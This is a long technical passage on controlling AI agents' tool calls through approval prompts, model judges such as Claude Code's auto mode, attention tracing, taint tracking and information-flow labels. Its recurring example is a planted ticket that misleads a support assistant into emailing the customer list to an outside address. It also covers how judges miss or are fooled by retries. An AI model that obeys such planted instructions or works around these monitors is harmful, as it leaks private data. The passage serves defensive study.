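| What the server checks | Specification | Standard server in the Python kit |
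|---|---|---|
| Nobody has altered the state | MUST, if the state affects authorization, access to resources or business logic | Included |
| The same principal is calling | SHOULD | Included if the kit validated an access token |
| The request and its important arguments are the same | SHOULD | Included, using the method, tool name and a hash of the arguments |
| The state is recent | SHOULD | Included, with a limit of 600 seconds for each round |
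| Nobody has used the state before | MUST, where a second use would break a once-only operation | Not included |
| The user answered the same question | Not covered | Included for questions that the kit manages |

A server could meet every absolute requirement here and still accept an approval that was given for a different email. The user might approve sending the summary to her manager, and a compromised client could then attach the resulting state, unaltered, to a call that sends the customer list elsewhere. The server could detect the switch only by comparing the arguments, which is recommended but not required. The recommendations should be requirements for any gate whose approvals authorize something important.

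The Python defaults are good but have gaps that matter in a company. If a gateway checks the user's login and the server doesn't, the kit has no principal to compare, so its check on the principal does nothing unless the developer supplies an identity. Each copy of the server also generates its own secret key by default, so a repeated call that reaches a different copy fails unless the developer gives all the copies the same key. Developers who use the kit's low-level server get none of these protections unless they add them.

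The server has to keep a record of used approvals to stop one from being used twice, since a copied state looks the same as the original. Liu's HCP includes a random number in each approval, marks it as used before the tool runs, and rejects any later call with the same number. Like the OpenID Foundation's draft, it also rechecks permissions once the approval arrives. The record of used numbers covers only one process and is lost in a crash, so a service with several copies would need a shared database. This is worth the trouble for a payment or an email, but a search can be repeated without harm.

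### What a valid approval proves

Passing all these checks shows that the approval answers a question the server issued and came back unaltered, for the same user and the same call, but not that a person read the question. Liu makes this point about the cryptographic code that protects the state, which establishes integrity and binding but not genuine review.

In the Python kit's documentation, the example client answers a server's question with a value written into the program, without asking a person. The server receives the same kind of message it would get if a user had thought about the question and answered it. A server that relies on approvals therefore trusts the host to show the question to the user and report the answer accurately.

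A real click also doesn't prove that the person understood the call. One developer interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) said they had approved an action and the agent then did something different from what they expected.

### What the email prompt should show

The planted ticket triggers the prompt at a convenient time for the attacker, because the user has just asked the assistant to send an email and expects a request to approve one. If the host displays only "Allow `send_email`?", she can't tell that anything is wrong, and approving it is reasonable.

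The mail server's question is better because it includes the address. She might still take `records@outside.example` for an archive that her company uses. A fuller prompt would give her more to go on:

```text
Send an email outside the company?

To:        records@outside.example (first email to this address)
Contains:  412 customer records: names, email addresses, phone numbers
Undo:      not possible after sending
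```

She asked for a ticket summary, so the second line should stop her if she reads it. Ordinary software should produce that line from the call's arguments rather than the assistant's own model, because a model that has followed the planted instruction might describe the customer list as a "ticket summary". Showing the full body is useful too, but she may not scroll through hundreds of lines. For a mailing list, the prompt should name the outside members.

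Such effects are much harder to display for code. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) gives the example of a prompt for `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine, but approving it authorises whatever is in that file. In the paper's collection of 290 incident reports, user review was a contributing factor in 105. In 80 of these the user had set the agent to run without asking, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative, with some reports in both groups. People mostly report things that went wrong, so these counts don't measure how often approvals fail. A better display can make prompts more informative, but it doesn't help when the user has turned them off.

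In the email case, a prompt before the call to `read_customers` might have been more useful. The assistant had to make that call before it could send the list, and the call has no obvious connection with summarising tickets. But hosts often allow read-only calls without a prompt, and users prefer this. In the survey by Salerno and colleagues, 98.1% of respondents were more willing to grant read-only access than other permissions.

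### How people respond to prompts

Anthropic reports that users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. Most of the commands are probably safe, and a careful user would approve them too, so that figure alone doesn't prove carelessness. An experiment Anthropic commissioned gives better evidence of how carefully people check. A research vendor had 1,053 paid testers work on coding tasks in a test environment, and replaced one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

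Anthropic published these results to justify replacing prompts with its classifier. The testers also weren't working on their own projects, and a developer with her own files at stake might be more careful. Part of the fall from 17% to 5% may have occurred because the people who got through 50 prompts were hasty from the start. The early figure is more worrying, because about five in six testers approved the dangerous command before they had seen many prompts, so fatigue can't be the whole explanation.

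Developers describe themselves as more careful. Salerno and colleagues interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed another 115, of whom 107 answered the questions about permissions. Of these, 47.7% said they read prompts carefully, 33.6% said they skimmed them, and 20.6% said they approved by default. A third said they had become less careful over time. The 47.7% and 13.6% figures come from different samples, so they can't show how many people overrate their own care, but the gap between them suggests that some do.

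This problem existed before agents, with Android permissions and browser warnings. Salerno and colleagues review research which found that people often overlook or misunderstand such messages, and that repeated exposure makes them pay less attention.

In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 US participants from outside the software industry supervise a simulated assistant through a day of 18 actions. Eleven were necessary for the tasks, and seven went beyond them, such as reading bank transactions to help with a travel budget. Every prompt described the action in plain language, including the data, recipient or amount. One group was asked to approve each action, another was prompted only when a model escalated an action, and the third first wrote standing rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of consequence.

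| | Approve every action | Model escalates some actions | Standing rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Participants | 34 | 44 | 35 |
| Average prompts per person | 18.0 | 10.0 | 10.9 |
| Share of the extra actions blocked | 59.6% | 53.9% | 39.6% |
| Approval rate when an extra action caused a prompt | 40.3% | 46.1% | 66.8% |

Some of these approvals were harmless. In the first group, 30 of 34 participants let the assistant phone the airport to confirm a flight, which many travellers would welcome. But 12 of the 34 also let it read private messages it didn't need for the task, even though the prompt described the action clearly.

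The standing-rules group did the worst, although the rules were meant to give people more control. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so most decisions came back to them as prompts. Of the 148 extra actions that went ahead in this group, participants had approved 133. The approval rate in the last row makes this group look slightly too permissive, because its "never" rules had already blocked some actions that cautious people would have refused, but that doesn't explain why the group blocked fewer actions overall. Yan's experiment can't isolate the cause, because the three designs differed in several ways and the later recruits all went into the standing-rules group. After correction for multiple comparisons, only the difference from the first group remained statistically reliable.

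### When human approval is worth asking for

The best argument for asking the user is that she knows what she wants. She can recognize, for example, that the deputy should get the summary because the manager is on holiday, which a rule can't detect. People report using this knowledge; in Salerno and colleagues' survey, 67.3% said they were less likely to grant a request that didn't fit the task.

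The arguments against human approval are volume, habit and incomplete displays. In Yan's first group, people spent an average of 142 seconds on 18 prompts, or about eight seconds each. At that pace, approving 200 calls a day would take about 26 minutes. One interviewed developer complained that clicking something every ten seconds defeats the purpose of a faster tool. Someone in that position will probably switch the prompts off, which leaves the gate without a human check.

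The usual response is to prompt less often, which saves effort but may not improve the remaining answers. Yan's two groups with fewer prompts didn't block more of the extra actions than the group asked to approve every action. Those sessions were short, though, so they provide little evidence about someone who has been answering prompts all week.

Showing consequences should help more, since people can't object to a recipient they can't see. But even with clear descriptions, participants in Yan's first group approved two in five of the extra actions. The software also has to identify the consequences correctly. Yan built a proxy that uses a language model to label tools by their likely effects, such as spending money or deleting something. In a simulation where the user had forbidden one kind of action, the proxy failed to stop 14% of the tools of that kind.

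A third reply is to reserve approval for actions that are hard to undo. Anthropic's data offer some support for this, since users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. They may reject a plan because they dislike its design rather than because it is dangerous, but they are evidently reading it. Even with its classifier as the default, Anthropic recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

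The support assistant could then read open tickets and email colleagues without prompting the user. The gate would refuse `outside.example` automatically because no grant covers it, so the user would not have to spot the trick. It would prompt her only for emails to an approved outside recipient, such as the auditor, and would show her the contents. If she refuses, the host should ask whether she objects to this email or to sending the data out at all, a distinction that Salerno and colleagues recommend. Otherwise the agent may treat her refusal as applying only to that address and try another.

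## Using a model to judge whether a call fits the task

A user knows what she asked for, but she can't carefully check hundreds of calls a day, so the host can have a second language model check them all. Developers often call this model a judge or a classifier. The host holds each proposed call, gives the judge the call and some context, and runs the call only if the judge approves it.

After the planted ticket has misled the assistant, the judge might receive this:

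```text
Request:        Summarise the open tickets and email the summary to my manager.
Earlier calls:  read_tickets(status = "open")
                read_customers()
Proposed call:  send_email(to = "records@outside.example",
                           subject = "Customer list",
                           body = "Name, email, phone: ...")

Does the proposed call fit the request?
```

A capable model should answer no, because the request mentions neither customer records nor this address. It should also have rejected the `read_customers` call one step earlier. The main advantage of using a model as a judge is that nobody had to write a rule for either call.

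### What the judge should receive

More context helps a judge interpret a call, but some of that context may come from an attacker.

| Input | How it helps | How it can mislead |
|---|---|---|
| The user's messages | They state the task | The user may have pasted in text from an outsider |
| Earlier calls | They show how the agent got here | Their arguments may repeat planted text |
| Tool results | They show where a name or number came from | They are the usual route for planted text |
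| The agent's explanation | It may give a good reason for an odd call | A misled agent may argue for the attacker's call |

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a judge that receives only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. The host removes tool results to keep planted text away from the judge. It also removes the agent's messages, which could mislead the judge, for example by claiming that the user had implicitly approved an action earlier. In the support example, this judge could reject the call without reading the planted ticket, because sending out the customer list conflicts with the user's request whatever prompted it.

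The drawback is that the judge can't check where a value came from. If the assistant looks up the manager's address in the staff directory, the judge can't confirm that the address belongs to the manager without seeing the lookup result.

Anthropic also tested the judge with other combinations of inputs. Adding the agent's messages and the tool results made it worse at catching calls that went beyond the user's wishes. When it saw only the tool calls, it missed the fewest of these, but it also blocked actions that users had plainly requested.

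Some planted text can still reach the judge. If the assistant copies a passage from the ticket into an email, the judge sees that passage in the tool call's arguments. Delegating work to a second agent can also mislead the judge, because the first agent's instructions replace the user's messages and make the task look fully authorized. Claude Code therefore runs the judge at the handover, while the user's messages are still available, and again when the second agent returns its results.

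A judge of this kind fits most easily in the host, because it needs the user's request.

### How auto mode works

Anthropic first released auto mode as a research preview on its Team plan. It has since replaced most of Claude Code's permission prompts. In an update dated 22 October 2026, Anthropic announced that most Claude apps would also use auto mode by default.

1. Fixed rules allow tools that can't change anything, such as file searches, and calls that match the user's own narrow permissions. Auto mode sets aside broad permissions, such as one to run any Python program, because they would exempt the most dangerous commands from the check.
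2. Edits to files inside the project folder also run without the judge, since the developer can review them through version control.
3. The judge receives every other call, including shell commands, web requests and calls to outside tools. It gives a one-word answer, and its instructions tell it to lean towards blocking.
4. If the answer is to block, the same model gets the same input again, with an instruction to reason carefully before it decides. The call runs if this second answer is favourable.

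The instructions tell the judge to consider what a command will do, however the agent has written it. If the agent writes a script and then runs it, the judge has to assess the script. The judge must also treat anything the agent chose by itself as unauthorized until the user says otherwise. Under these instructions, "clean up my branches" doesn't authorize deleting a whole batch of them, and "can we fix this?" is a question rather than permission to make changes.

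More than twenty rules block dangerous actions such as sending internal data outside or switching off logging. By default, the judge trusts only the code repository the user is working in. A company can add its own trusted systems, blocked categories and exceptions.

When the model refuses a call, the agent receives the reason and an instruction to look for a safer way. After three refusals in a row, or twenty in a session, the host prompts the user. If the agent is running without a user interface, the host ends the process instead.

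### False stops and misses

Anthropic tested the judge on three sets of calls when it ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6. Anthropic measured false stops on 10,000 real calls from its employees' sessions. It measured misses on 52 real actions in which Claude had gone beyond what an employee wanted, and on 1,000 generated attempts to leak data.

| | False stops, real calls | Misses, overeager actions | Misses, data leaks |
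|---|---|---|---|
| One-word answer only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| With the second, reasoned answer | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second answer removes about 95% of the false stops but more than doubles the misses. The 17% miss rate is the most relevant to everyday use, but also the least certain. It represents about nine misses in only 52 actions, so a standard 95% interval runs from roughly 9% to 30%. Anthropic collected these actions from sessions where an employee had refused the call or someone had flagged it later, so the set leaves out dangerous actions that nobody noticed. Those may also be harder for a judge to catch.

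In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the judge had identified the danger but accepted weak evidence of consent. For example, it treated a user's request to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) as permission for a force-push, which overwrites the code's existing history. In other cases, it relied on the user's earlier approval of one similar action. Anthropic reworded the judge's instructions but found no fix whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks. Other judges probably share this weakness, because people rarely specify how much they are permitting.

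### Later tests of auto mode

In August, Anthropic published more favourable results. In its experiment, paid testers refused only 13.6% of clearly dangerous commands, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Auto mode blocked 800 commands that the testers approved and allowed six that they refused. The commands in this experiment were easier to recognise than the overeager actions, many of which look like reasonable steps towards the user's goal.

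Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, then tested the judge with synthetic attacks inserted into real coding sessions. Anthropic responded mainly by giving the judge more facts about its surroundings, such as whether a code repository is public. Across all the attacks, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. This suggests that a good compromise is to give the judge facts the host can collect itself, without the agent's explanations or whole tool results.

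Anthropic also compared sessions that its safety systems had flagged for review. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. This evidence is weaker because a model graded the harm, and because users chose their own mode and may have used manual approval for riskier work.

Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to run 72 planted-instruction scenarios, ten times each, against agents that controlled a browser through MCP tools. No attack succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. But only 0.09% succeeded against Anthropic's latest models with all permission checks off, so the result is little evidence of how well the judge works.

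The same tests show a larger difference for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Attacks succeeded 19.03% of the time when the model had full access in the coding tool Codex, and 5.83% with Codex's Auto-review mode on. OpenAI has since released a new version of Auto-review, so the 5.83% figure may be out of date.

Anthropic's August post doesn't give a new false-stop rate for ordinary calls. The earlier rate of 0.4% may not apply to the current judge, which has had several changes to make it stricter.

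### Reading a model's scores

A judge doesn't have to write out its verdict. Before a language model produces a word, it gives each possible next word a score, called a logit. Son (2026), in *Governed MCP*, uses these scores in a gate built into Anima OS, an experimental operating system. The gate gives a model the proposed call and asks whether the action is dangerous, harmful or a privacy violation. It then computes

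$$s = \text{logit}(\text{Dangerous}) - \text{logit}(\text{Safe})$$

and corrects the result for any general preference the model has for one of the two words. It converts s into a confidence between 0 and 1. Above 0.90 it refuses the call, and between 0.70 and 0.90 it allows the call but logs a warning.

Son tested the full gate, which combines the model with several kinds of fixed rules, on 101 calls that he had labelled himself. It caught 30 of 37 dangerous calls and wrongly stopped nine of 64 harmless ones. The rules alone caught only ten of the dangerous calls and, judging by Son's published accuracy scores, also wrongly stopped nine harmless ones. Adding the model therefore caught 20 more dangerous calls without increasing the total number of false stops. That is a good result for the model, although a different author might have written better rules or harder test cases.

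The false-stop rate also depends heavily on the test. The gate, with extra hand-written rules, stopped no safe action in a test of 260 operating-system actions. XSTest is a public collection of chat questions that includes safe ones that sound dangerous. The scoring method alone flagged 52% to 86% of the safe questions, depending on the model. These aren't tool calls, but a support team's emails may also contain alarming words for harmless reasons.

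This gate runs below the application, where the agent's code can't skip or replace the check. Six low-level routes to data or the network still bypass it. The model also receives the call without the user's request, which is a greater limitation for judging task fit. It might flag an email full of customer records, but it would have no basis for flagging a ticket summary sent to the wrong colleague.

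### Measuring the distance from the request

Errico (2026), in *Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)*, proposes a direct comparison between the call and the user's original request. It uses an embedding model, which turns a text into a list of numbers so that texts with similar meanings get similar lists. For the original request r₀ and the agent's nth action aₙ, the semantic distance is

$$d(r_0, a_n) = 1 - \cos\big(e(r_0), e(a_n)\big)$$

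where e gives the list of numbers for a text. The distance is 0 if the two lists point in the same direction and 1 if they are unrelated. When it passes a threshold, the gate can raise an alert, hold the call or ask a person. Errico also recommends tracking the drift over a whole series of calls, because several small steps can lead a long way from the request.

AARM is a specification, and Errico reports no test of this measure. He leaves the thresholds to each deployment and the measurements to future studies. The distance check is recommended (SHOULD) rather than required, so a product can claim to comply with AARM without it.

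The measure may not work well alone, because embeddings mostly reflect what a text is about. A call that sends the ticket summary to a competitor would probably be about as far from the request as one that sends it to the manager. But a sensible step, such as checking the holiday calendar to find the manager's deputy, might be far from the request.

### Tracing what influenced the agent

*MINDGUARD* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) presents MindGuard, a system that examines the agent's own model while the model writes a call. It is meant to catch instructions planted in tool descriptions, such as the time-zone server's instruction that redirected payments. MindGuard uses attention, the mechanism that determines how strongly a model draws on each earlier piece of text as it writes the next.

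MindGuard collects the attention values and removes words that attract attention whatever the task. It then adds up the squares of the remaining values for each source, which gives the source's influence w. For every tool that the agent did not call, it computes

$$\text{ratio} = \frac{w(\text{description of the uncalled tool})}{w(\text{user's request}) + w(\text{description of the called tool})}$$

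A high ratio means that an unused tool's description strongly influenced the call. In the time-zone case, MindGuard could stop the payment and identify the description responsible.

The threshold for this ratio determines the balance between catches and false stops. These results are for Qwen3-8b, a small open model:

| Threshold | Poisoned calls caught | False stops, no poisoned description present | False stops, poisoned description present but without effect |
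|---|---|---|---|
| 0.5 | 97.1% | 1.5% | 13.1% |
| 0.9 | 91.2% | 0.0% | 0.9% |

The catch rates come from only 68 poisoned calls. With the model's step-by-step reasoning on, the higher threshold caught 87.4% of 289 poisoned calls and wrongly stopped 0.4% of ordinary ones. Across the models tested, MindGuard identified the right tool for at least 95% of the attacks it caught. It added less than a second and needed no extra model call.

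An attacker can't get past MindGuard simply with a persuasive argument, because it doesn't interpret text as a judge model does. Wang and colleagues argue, but don't test, that an attacker would struggle to write an instruction that works while drawing little of the model's attention. They also acknowledge that attention isn't strictly a cause of the model's choice. MindGuard needs access to the model's internal values, so only the model's provider or someone running an open model can use it.

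The ratio would not flag the planted ticket, because the ticket is a tool result and the ratio covers only descriptions. MindGuard also traces the influence of results, so a company could add a rule that an email's recipient must come from the user. An honest description could also cause a legitimate call to be stopped. For example, if the description of `read_customers` advises calling that tool before `send_email`, the description may legitimately influence an email call.

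### How many stops are right

Even an accurate judge can be wrong about most of the calls it blocks, because unwanted calls are rare. Suppose an agent makes 10,000 calls and 10 of them are unwanted. A judge that catches 80% of unwanted calls blocks eight of the 10. If it also wrongly blocks 0.5% of the 9,990 wanted calls, that adds about 50 more. Only eight of the roughly 58 blocked calls, or about 14%, are unwanted.

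In general, if b is the share of calls that are unwanted, c the catch rate and f the false-stop rate, then

$$\text{share of stops that are right} = \frac{bc}{bc + (1-b)f}$$

The table repeats the calculation with published rates. Every row assumes 10 unwanted calls in 10,000, which is not a measured figure.

| Judge | Catch rate | False-stop rate | Caught | Missed | Wrongly stopped | Stops that are right |
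|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Illustration | 80% | 0.5% | 8 | 2 | 50 | 14% |
| Auto mode, one-word answer only | 93.4% | 8.5% | 9.3 | 0.7 | 849 | 1% |
| Auto mode, both answers | 83% | 0.4% | 8.3 | 1.7 | 40 | 17% |
| Governed MCP, full gate | 81% | 14% | 8.1 | 1.9 | 1,405 | 0.6% |
| MindGuard, threshold 0.9, with reasoning | 87.4% | 0.4% | 8.7 | 1.3 | 40 | 18% |

The rows show how much the false-stop rate matters. Auto mode's second answer adds one miss but prevents about 800 false stops. The rows can't be used to rank the systems, because each system faced different attacks and harmless calls.

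The assumed number of unwanted calls matters just as much. At auto mode's final rates, 68% of stops would be correct if 100 of every 10,000 calls were unwanted, but just 2% if only 1 was. A judge will therefore look much better in a test with many attacks than in an office where attacks are rare.

Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production* reports that one customer saw a refusal in roughly 10% of its sessions, and presents this as evidence that the judge stops unwanted calls. But at a false-stop rate of 0.4%, a session with 26 harmless calls has about a 10% chance of at least one refusal, so false stops alone could explain the customer's figure. The customer would have to review a sample of the refusals to find out whether any of the calls were unwanted.

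A judge can still be useful when most of its stops are wrong. If the refusal goes back to the agent, a false stop usually leads to one retry. If refusals go to a person instead, that person reviews about 48 prompts rather than 10,000, and one in six concerns a real problem rather than one in a thousand, which should help with approval fatigue.

### What a judge adds to fixed rules

The best argument for a judge is that it can assess calls nobody foresaw. Anthropic describes an incident in which Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead. Auto mode stopped the attempt. A fixed rule would have done so only if someone had thought to block that site, and it would also stop users who want to publish there. Auto mode also stopped Claude when a user asked for read-only access to billing data and Claude chose a role with full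 control of the cloud account.

A judge can also permit wanted work that narrow rules block, such as the email to the manager's deputy.

Besides making the errors already described, a model delays each call it checks. Son measured 358 milliseconds per check with one model, so one machine can check fewer than three calls a second. His fixed rules and logging together took about 0.01 milliseconds. Llama Guard 3, a safety model that writes out its verdict, took between 851 and 1,142 milliseconds on the same machine. Auto mode limits the delay by having its model first answer in one word and write out its reasoning only for calls that fail that check.

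Verdicts can also vary. *MCPShield* (Zhou, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) uses a model for a different purpose, to judge from trial calls whether a server behaves as described. With one agent model and one set of malicious servers, the system stopped between 66.7% and 100% of attacks, apparently across repeated runs. Changing a judge can also alter its verdicts. After Anthropic's improvements, auto mode missed about 2% of the held-out Apollo attacks that it had previously caught. An administrator therefore can't assume that the judge will refuse a call today because it refused the same call last month.

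A misled agent may also retry a refused call in a different form. If a judge misses 17% of unwanted calls and each attempt is independent, at least one of three attempts gets through 43% of the time. Real attempts aren't independent, since a judge that refuses one version will probably refuse a similar one. Still, the added risk is a good reason to limit retries, as auto mode does.

Planted text that misleads the agent probably has the greatest chance of misleading the judge too when both are the same model. Governed MCP uses one loaded model for both, although it runs the check separately from the agent's conversation.

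### Combining rules with a judge

Since rules are predictable and a judge is flexible, a gate can apply the rules first and use the judge only for what remains:

```text
if a rule forbids the call, or no grant covers it:   refuse
else if a rule marks the call as low-risk:           run
else if the judge finds that it fits the task:       run
else:                                                refuse and tell the agent why

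after repeated refusals:                             ask the user
```

In this arrangement, the judge can block calls that the rules permit but can't override a refusal, so an attacker who fools it can get through only calls that the rules permit. The outcomes for the support assistant would be as follows.

| Proposed email | Rules | Judge | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ticket summary to the manager | Permit | Fits the request | Runs |
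| Customer list to a colleague | Permit | Doesn't fit | Refused |
| Customer list to `outside.example` | Refuse | Not consulted | Refused |

AARM allows a looser combination. It has a category of actions that the policy denies by default but the gate may permit, or send to a person, if the context clearly supports them. Errico's example is deleting records after the user has asked the agent to clean up her test data. This avoids wrongly blocking some calls, but it lets a mistaken judge widen the agent's permissions. Sending such cases to a person is safer when the action is hard to undo. AARM also lets the gate hold a call when it lacks the information to decide. If it still can't decide by the deadline, it refuses the call by default.

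Anthropic's auto mode has "hard deny" rules, which are designed to block actions such as sending secrets to outsiders, even if the user requests them. These rules work only if the judge model classifies the call correctly, so they are less reliable than a list of permitted addresses. A company that must keep its customer list private should also enforce this with a fixed rule.

The gate also needs a rule for when the judge is unavailable. Governed MCP fails closed, blocking every tool call. With the combination above, only calls that need the judge's verdict would have to wait.

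## Checking a sequence of calls and the data that moves between them

The support assistant is allowed to read the open tickets and the customer list, and an administrator might also let it email whoever filed a ticket. Each permission is reasonable on its own, but together they let the author of the planted ticket obtain the customer list, because a gate that compares each call with the assistant's permissions will allow all three.

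To stop this, a gate has to take account of what the agent has already done. *ToolGuardian* (2026), a rule system for tool calls, describes a similar case in which an agent reads records from a database and then updates a project page on GitHub. The task permits both calls, but ToolGuardian refuses the second because its rules forbid updating an outside service after a sensitive read unless someone has declared an exception.

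Attackers can exploit such combinations in many systems. Jiang, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *ChainCaps*, cite a study that found 365 multi-tool vulnerabilities in 19 of 20 real agent applications. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) cites reported success rates above 90% in STAC, a benchmark of attacks built from individually harmless calls.

### The lethal trifecta

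Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about AI security, uses the term "lethal trifecta" for three capabilities that together make data theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. The support assistant has all three, through the customer list, the tickets and the mail server respectively.

In 2025, the security company Invariant Labs demonstrated the problem using GitHub's MCP server. As Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes the attack, an outsider opens an issue (a problem report) in a public code repository and asks in it for information from a private one. When the repository's owner later has her coding assistant handle the issue, the assistant, which can read both repositories, fetches the private information and posts it as a public comment. The GitHub server alone let the assistant read the outsider's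 text, read private data and post publicly.

Other attacks combine several servers. The Model Context Protocol post on annotations describes one that used a malicious calendar event, a calendar server and a tool for running code. Users often connect tools from several sources in one session, and the post notes that the risk depends on the whole set. For example, one can't judge whether a tool that searches email is safe without knowing what else the agent can do.

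Removing any one of the three capabilities prevents this kind of theft. If the assistant only summarises tickets, the host can disconnect the customer list. If the assistant needs all three capabilities, the gate can track which ones it has used so far.

### Marking a whole conversation

Taint tracking records whether data or a session has touched untrusted or private material. The simplest version keeps two marks for each conversation. The gate stores them under its own key because MCP no longer has sessions. For the support assistant, the rules might be as follows.

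| Marks so far | After reading a ticket | After reading the customer list | Email to an outside address |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | Untrusted | Private | Allow |
| Untrusted | No change | Untrusted and private | Allow |
| Private | Untrusted and private | No change | Allow |
| Untrusted and private | No change | No change | Refuse, or hold for approval |

In the attack, `read_tickets` adds the first mark and `read_customers` adds the second. The gate then stops the email to `records@outside.example` without inspecting its body or recognising the planted instruction. It still allows email to colleagues, so the manager gets her summary. The marks stay until the conversation ends, because the model may later use anything it has read. The gate should set each mark before passing the result to the model, so the model can't act on the result first.

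The third row allows outside email because no untrusted text has reached the agent. A company that wants to prevent honest mistakes as well as attacks could block that email too.

*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) tested a similar rule, called toxic flow, with an agent based on GPT-4.1-mini. The attack failed in all five trials. This is a very small test, but the rule's result doesn't depend on which model proposes the email. The paper also tested a traditional military-style policy, in which the agent's clearance level determines what it may do. Toxic flow is more permissive because the agent can read any file, and only the resulting email may be blocked.

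### When the user wanted the email

Suppose the user asks the assistant to tell the outside auditor how many of this month's tickets came from customers on premium contracts. The assistant reads the tickets, looks up the contracts in the customer list and prepares an email containing only the count. The conversation now has both marks, as it did in the attack, so the gate stops the email.

The support team would have this problem constantly. The assistant usually replies to a customer after reading the ticket, which an outsider wrote, and the customer's record, which is private. If the gate holds all these replies for approval, the team will soon approve them out of habit. Starting a new conversation for each ticket prevents one customer's data from affecting the reply to another, but the assistant still has to read both the ticket and the record before replying.

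A more specific rule can help. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* proposes writing rules about sequences in temporal logic, a formal language for statements about time. The rule in the table above would look roughly like this:

$$\text{always}\big(\text{SendOutside} \rightarrow \neg(\text{once ReadUntrusted} \wedge \text{once ReadPrivate})\big)$$

Here "once" means "at some earlier point". The version of the logic in *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* can also refer to particular values and periods of time. An administrator could therefore forbid the agent from emailing one customer after it has read a different customer's record. This would allow ordinary replies and still stop the theft of the whole list. The existing program MonPoly can check such rules, so a company needn't write a new monitor for each one. But emailing the auditor's number would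 still break a rule against outside email after the agent has read the full list.

### Where the marks come from

To set the marks, a gate needs a record that `read_tickets` returns text written by outsiders and `read_customers` returns private data. An administrator can write this down for three servers but could hardly do so for thousands of tools, so several draft proposals would have servers supply the information.

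The broadest of these proposals on trust is SEP-1913, "Trust and Sensitivity Annotations", by Sam Morrow of GitHub and Robert Reichel of OpenAI. According to Model Context Protocol, the two companies based it on gaps they found while running MCP in production. It was still a draft in April 2026, when the MCP interest group on annotations listed it for discussion. Three narrower proposals, `unsafeOutputHint`, `secretHint` and `trustedHint`, address similar issues.

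A gate should let an unknown server's annotation add a mark but not prevent one, as with the existing hints. An annotation on the whole tool may also be too general, since a tool that reads files from GitHub can return public text from one repository and secrets from another. The interest group is still considering whether to let servers annotate each result as well.

Microsoft and GitHub have built an experimental version of this. With the feature on, GitHub's MCP server labels files and issues from public repositories "public" and "untrusted", and those from private repositories "private" and "trusted". It puts the labels in the `_meta` field of each result. GitHub's command-line assistant, Copilot CLI, has an experimental setting that combines these labels as results arrive and checks them before later calls, though only for some of the GitHub server's tools. Treating everything in a private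 repository as trusted is convenient but can be wrong, because an employee may have pasted in a customer's message.

Microsoft also suggests deriving labels from tools' existing hints. A gate could mark results from open-world tools as untrusted and results from tools that require a login as private. This needs no new standard, but the gate would miss the planted ticket if the ticket server's `openWorldHint` were false.

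### Labels on individual values

Instead of marking the conversation, a gate can label each piece of data. When a tool combines several pieces, the result gets a label at least as restrictive as each of theirs. If the inputs are x₁ to xₖ, then

$$\text{label}(y) = \text{label}(x_1) \sqcup \cdots \sqcup \text{label}(x_k)$$

where ⊔ means "combine cautiously". A result is untrusted if any input is untrusted. If a label lists the people who may read something, combining two labels keeps only the names on both lists.

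Microsoft gives an example with no attacker. Alex asks an agent to answer his email. Priya has sent him early sales figures, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see them yet, has written to ask about them. Only Alex and Priya may read Priya's message, and only Alex and Marco may read Marco's. A reply based on both messages has the label {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the agent can't send it to Marco without approval. If Priya had copied Marco into her message, his name would be on both lists and the agent could send him the reply without approval.

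A tool call may not show who will receive a message, as when it goes to a mailing list with outside members. Microsoft's sample policy for its chat service Teams therefore looks up the members of a channel before the agent posts there. If some of them aren't allowed to read the content, it prompts the user. But the policy skips this check when the agent has read nothing untrusted, so an agent could still post something in the wrong channel by mistake.

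Labels on values are hard to track through a language model. Once the model has read both emails, any word it writes might depend on either, and the gate can't determine which. The safe choice is to give everything the model writes the combined label of everything it has read. But this is as coarse as marking the whole conversation, and it brings back most of the false stops. Finer labels help only if the host keeps some of the data away from the model that chooses the calls.

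### CaMeL and Fides

CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), does this by separating the plan from the data. A planner turns the user's request into a program before it reads any untrusted text. For the ticket summary, the program might look like this:

```python
tickets = read_tickets(status="open")
summary = isolated_model("Summarise these tickets", tickets)
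send_email(to="manager@company.example", body=summary)
```

The second line uses a model that can read the tickets but can't call tools. The planted text may distort the summary, but it can't add a call to `read_customers` or change the recipient, because the program already fixes the calls and the recipient. As Liu explains, CaMeL also attaches capabilities to values to restrict where those values may go. A program written in advance is less flexible, though. It may not contain the right steps if one ticket turns out to need a refund and another a phone call.

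Microsoft's Fides, described in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025), lets the agent choose its next step as it goes. It builds on Willison's idea of having one model plan while an isolated second model reads untrusted text. The ticket summary would go through these steps.

1. The main model proposes `read_tickets`. The result is untrusted, so Fides stores it under a name such as `tickets_1` and shows the main model only the name.
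2. The main model asks the isolated model to summarise `tickets_1`. Fides stores the summary as `summary_1`, which is also untrusted.
3. The main model proposes an email to the manager with `summary_1` as the body.
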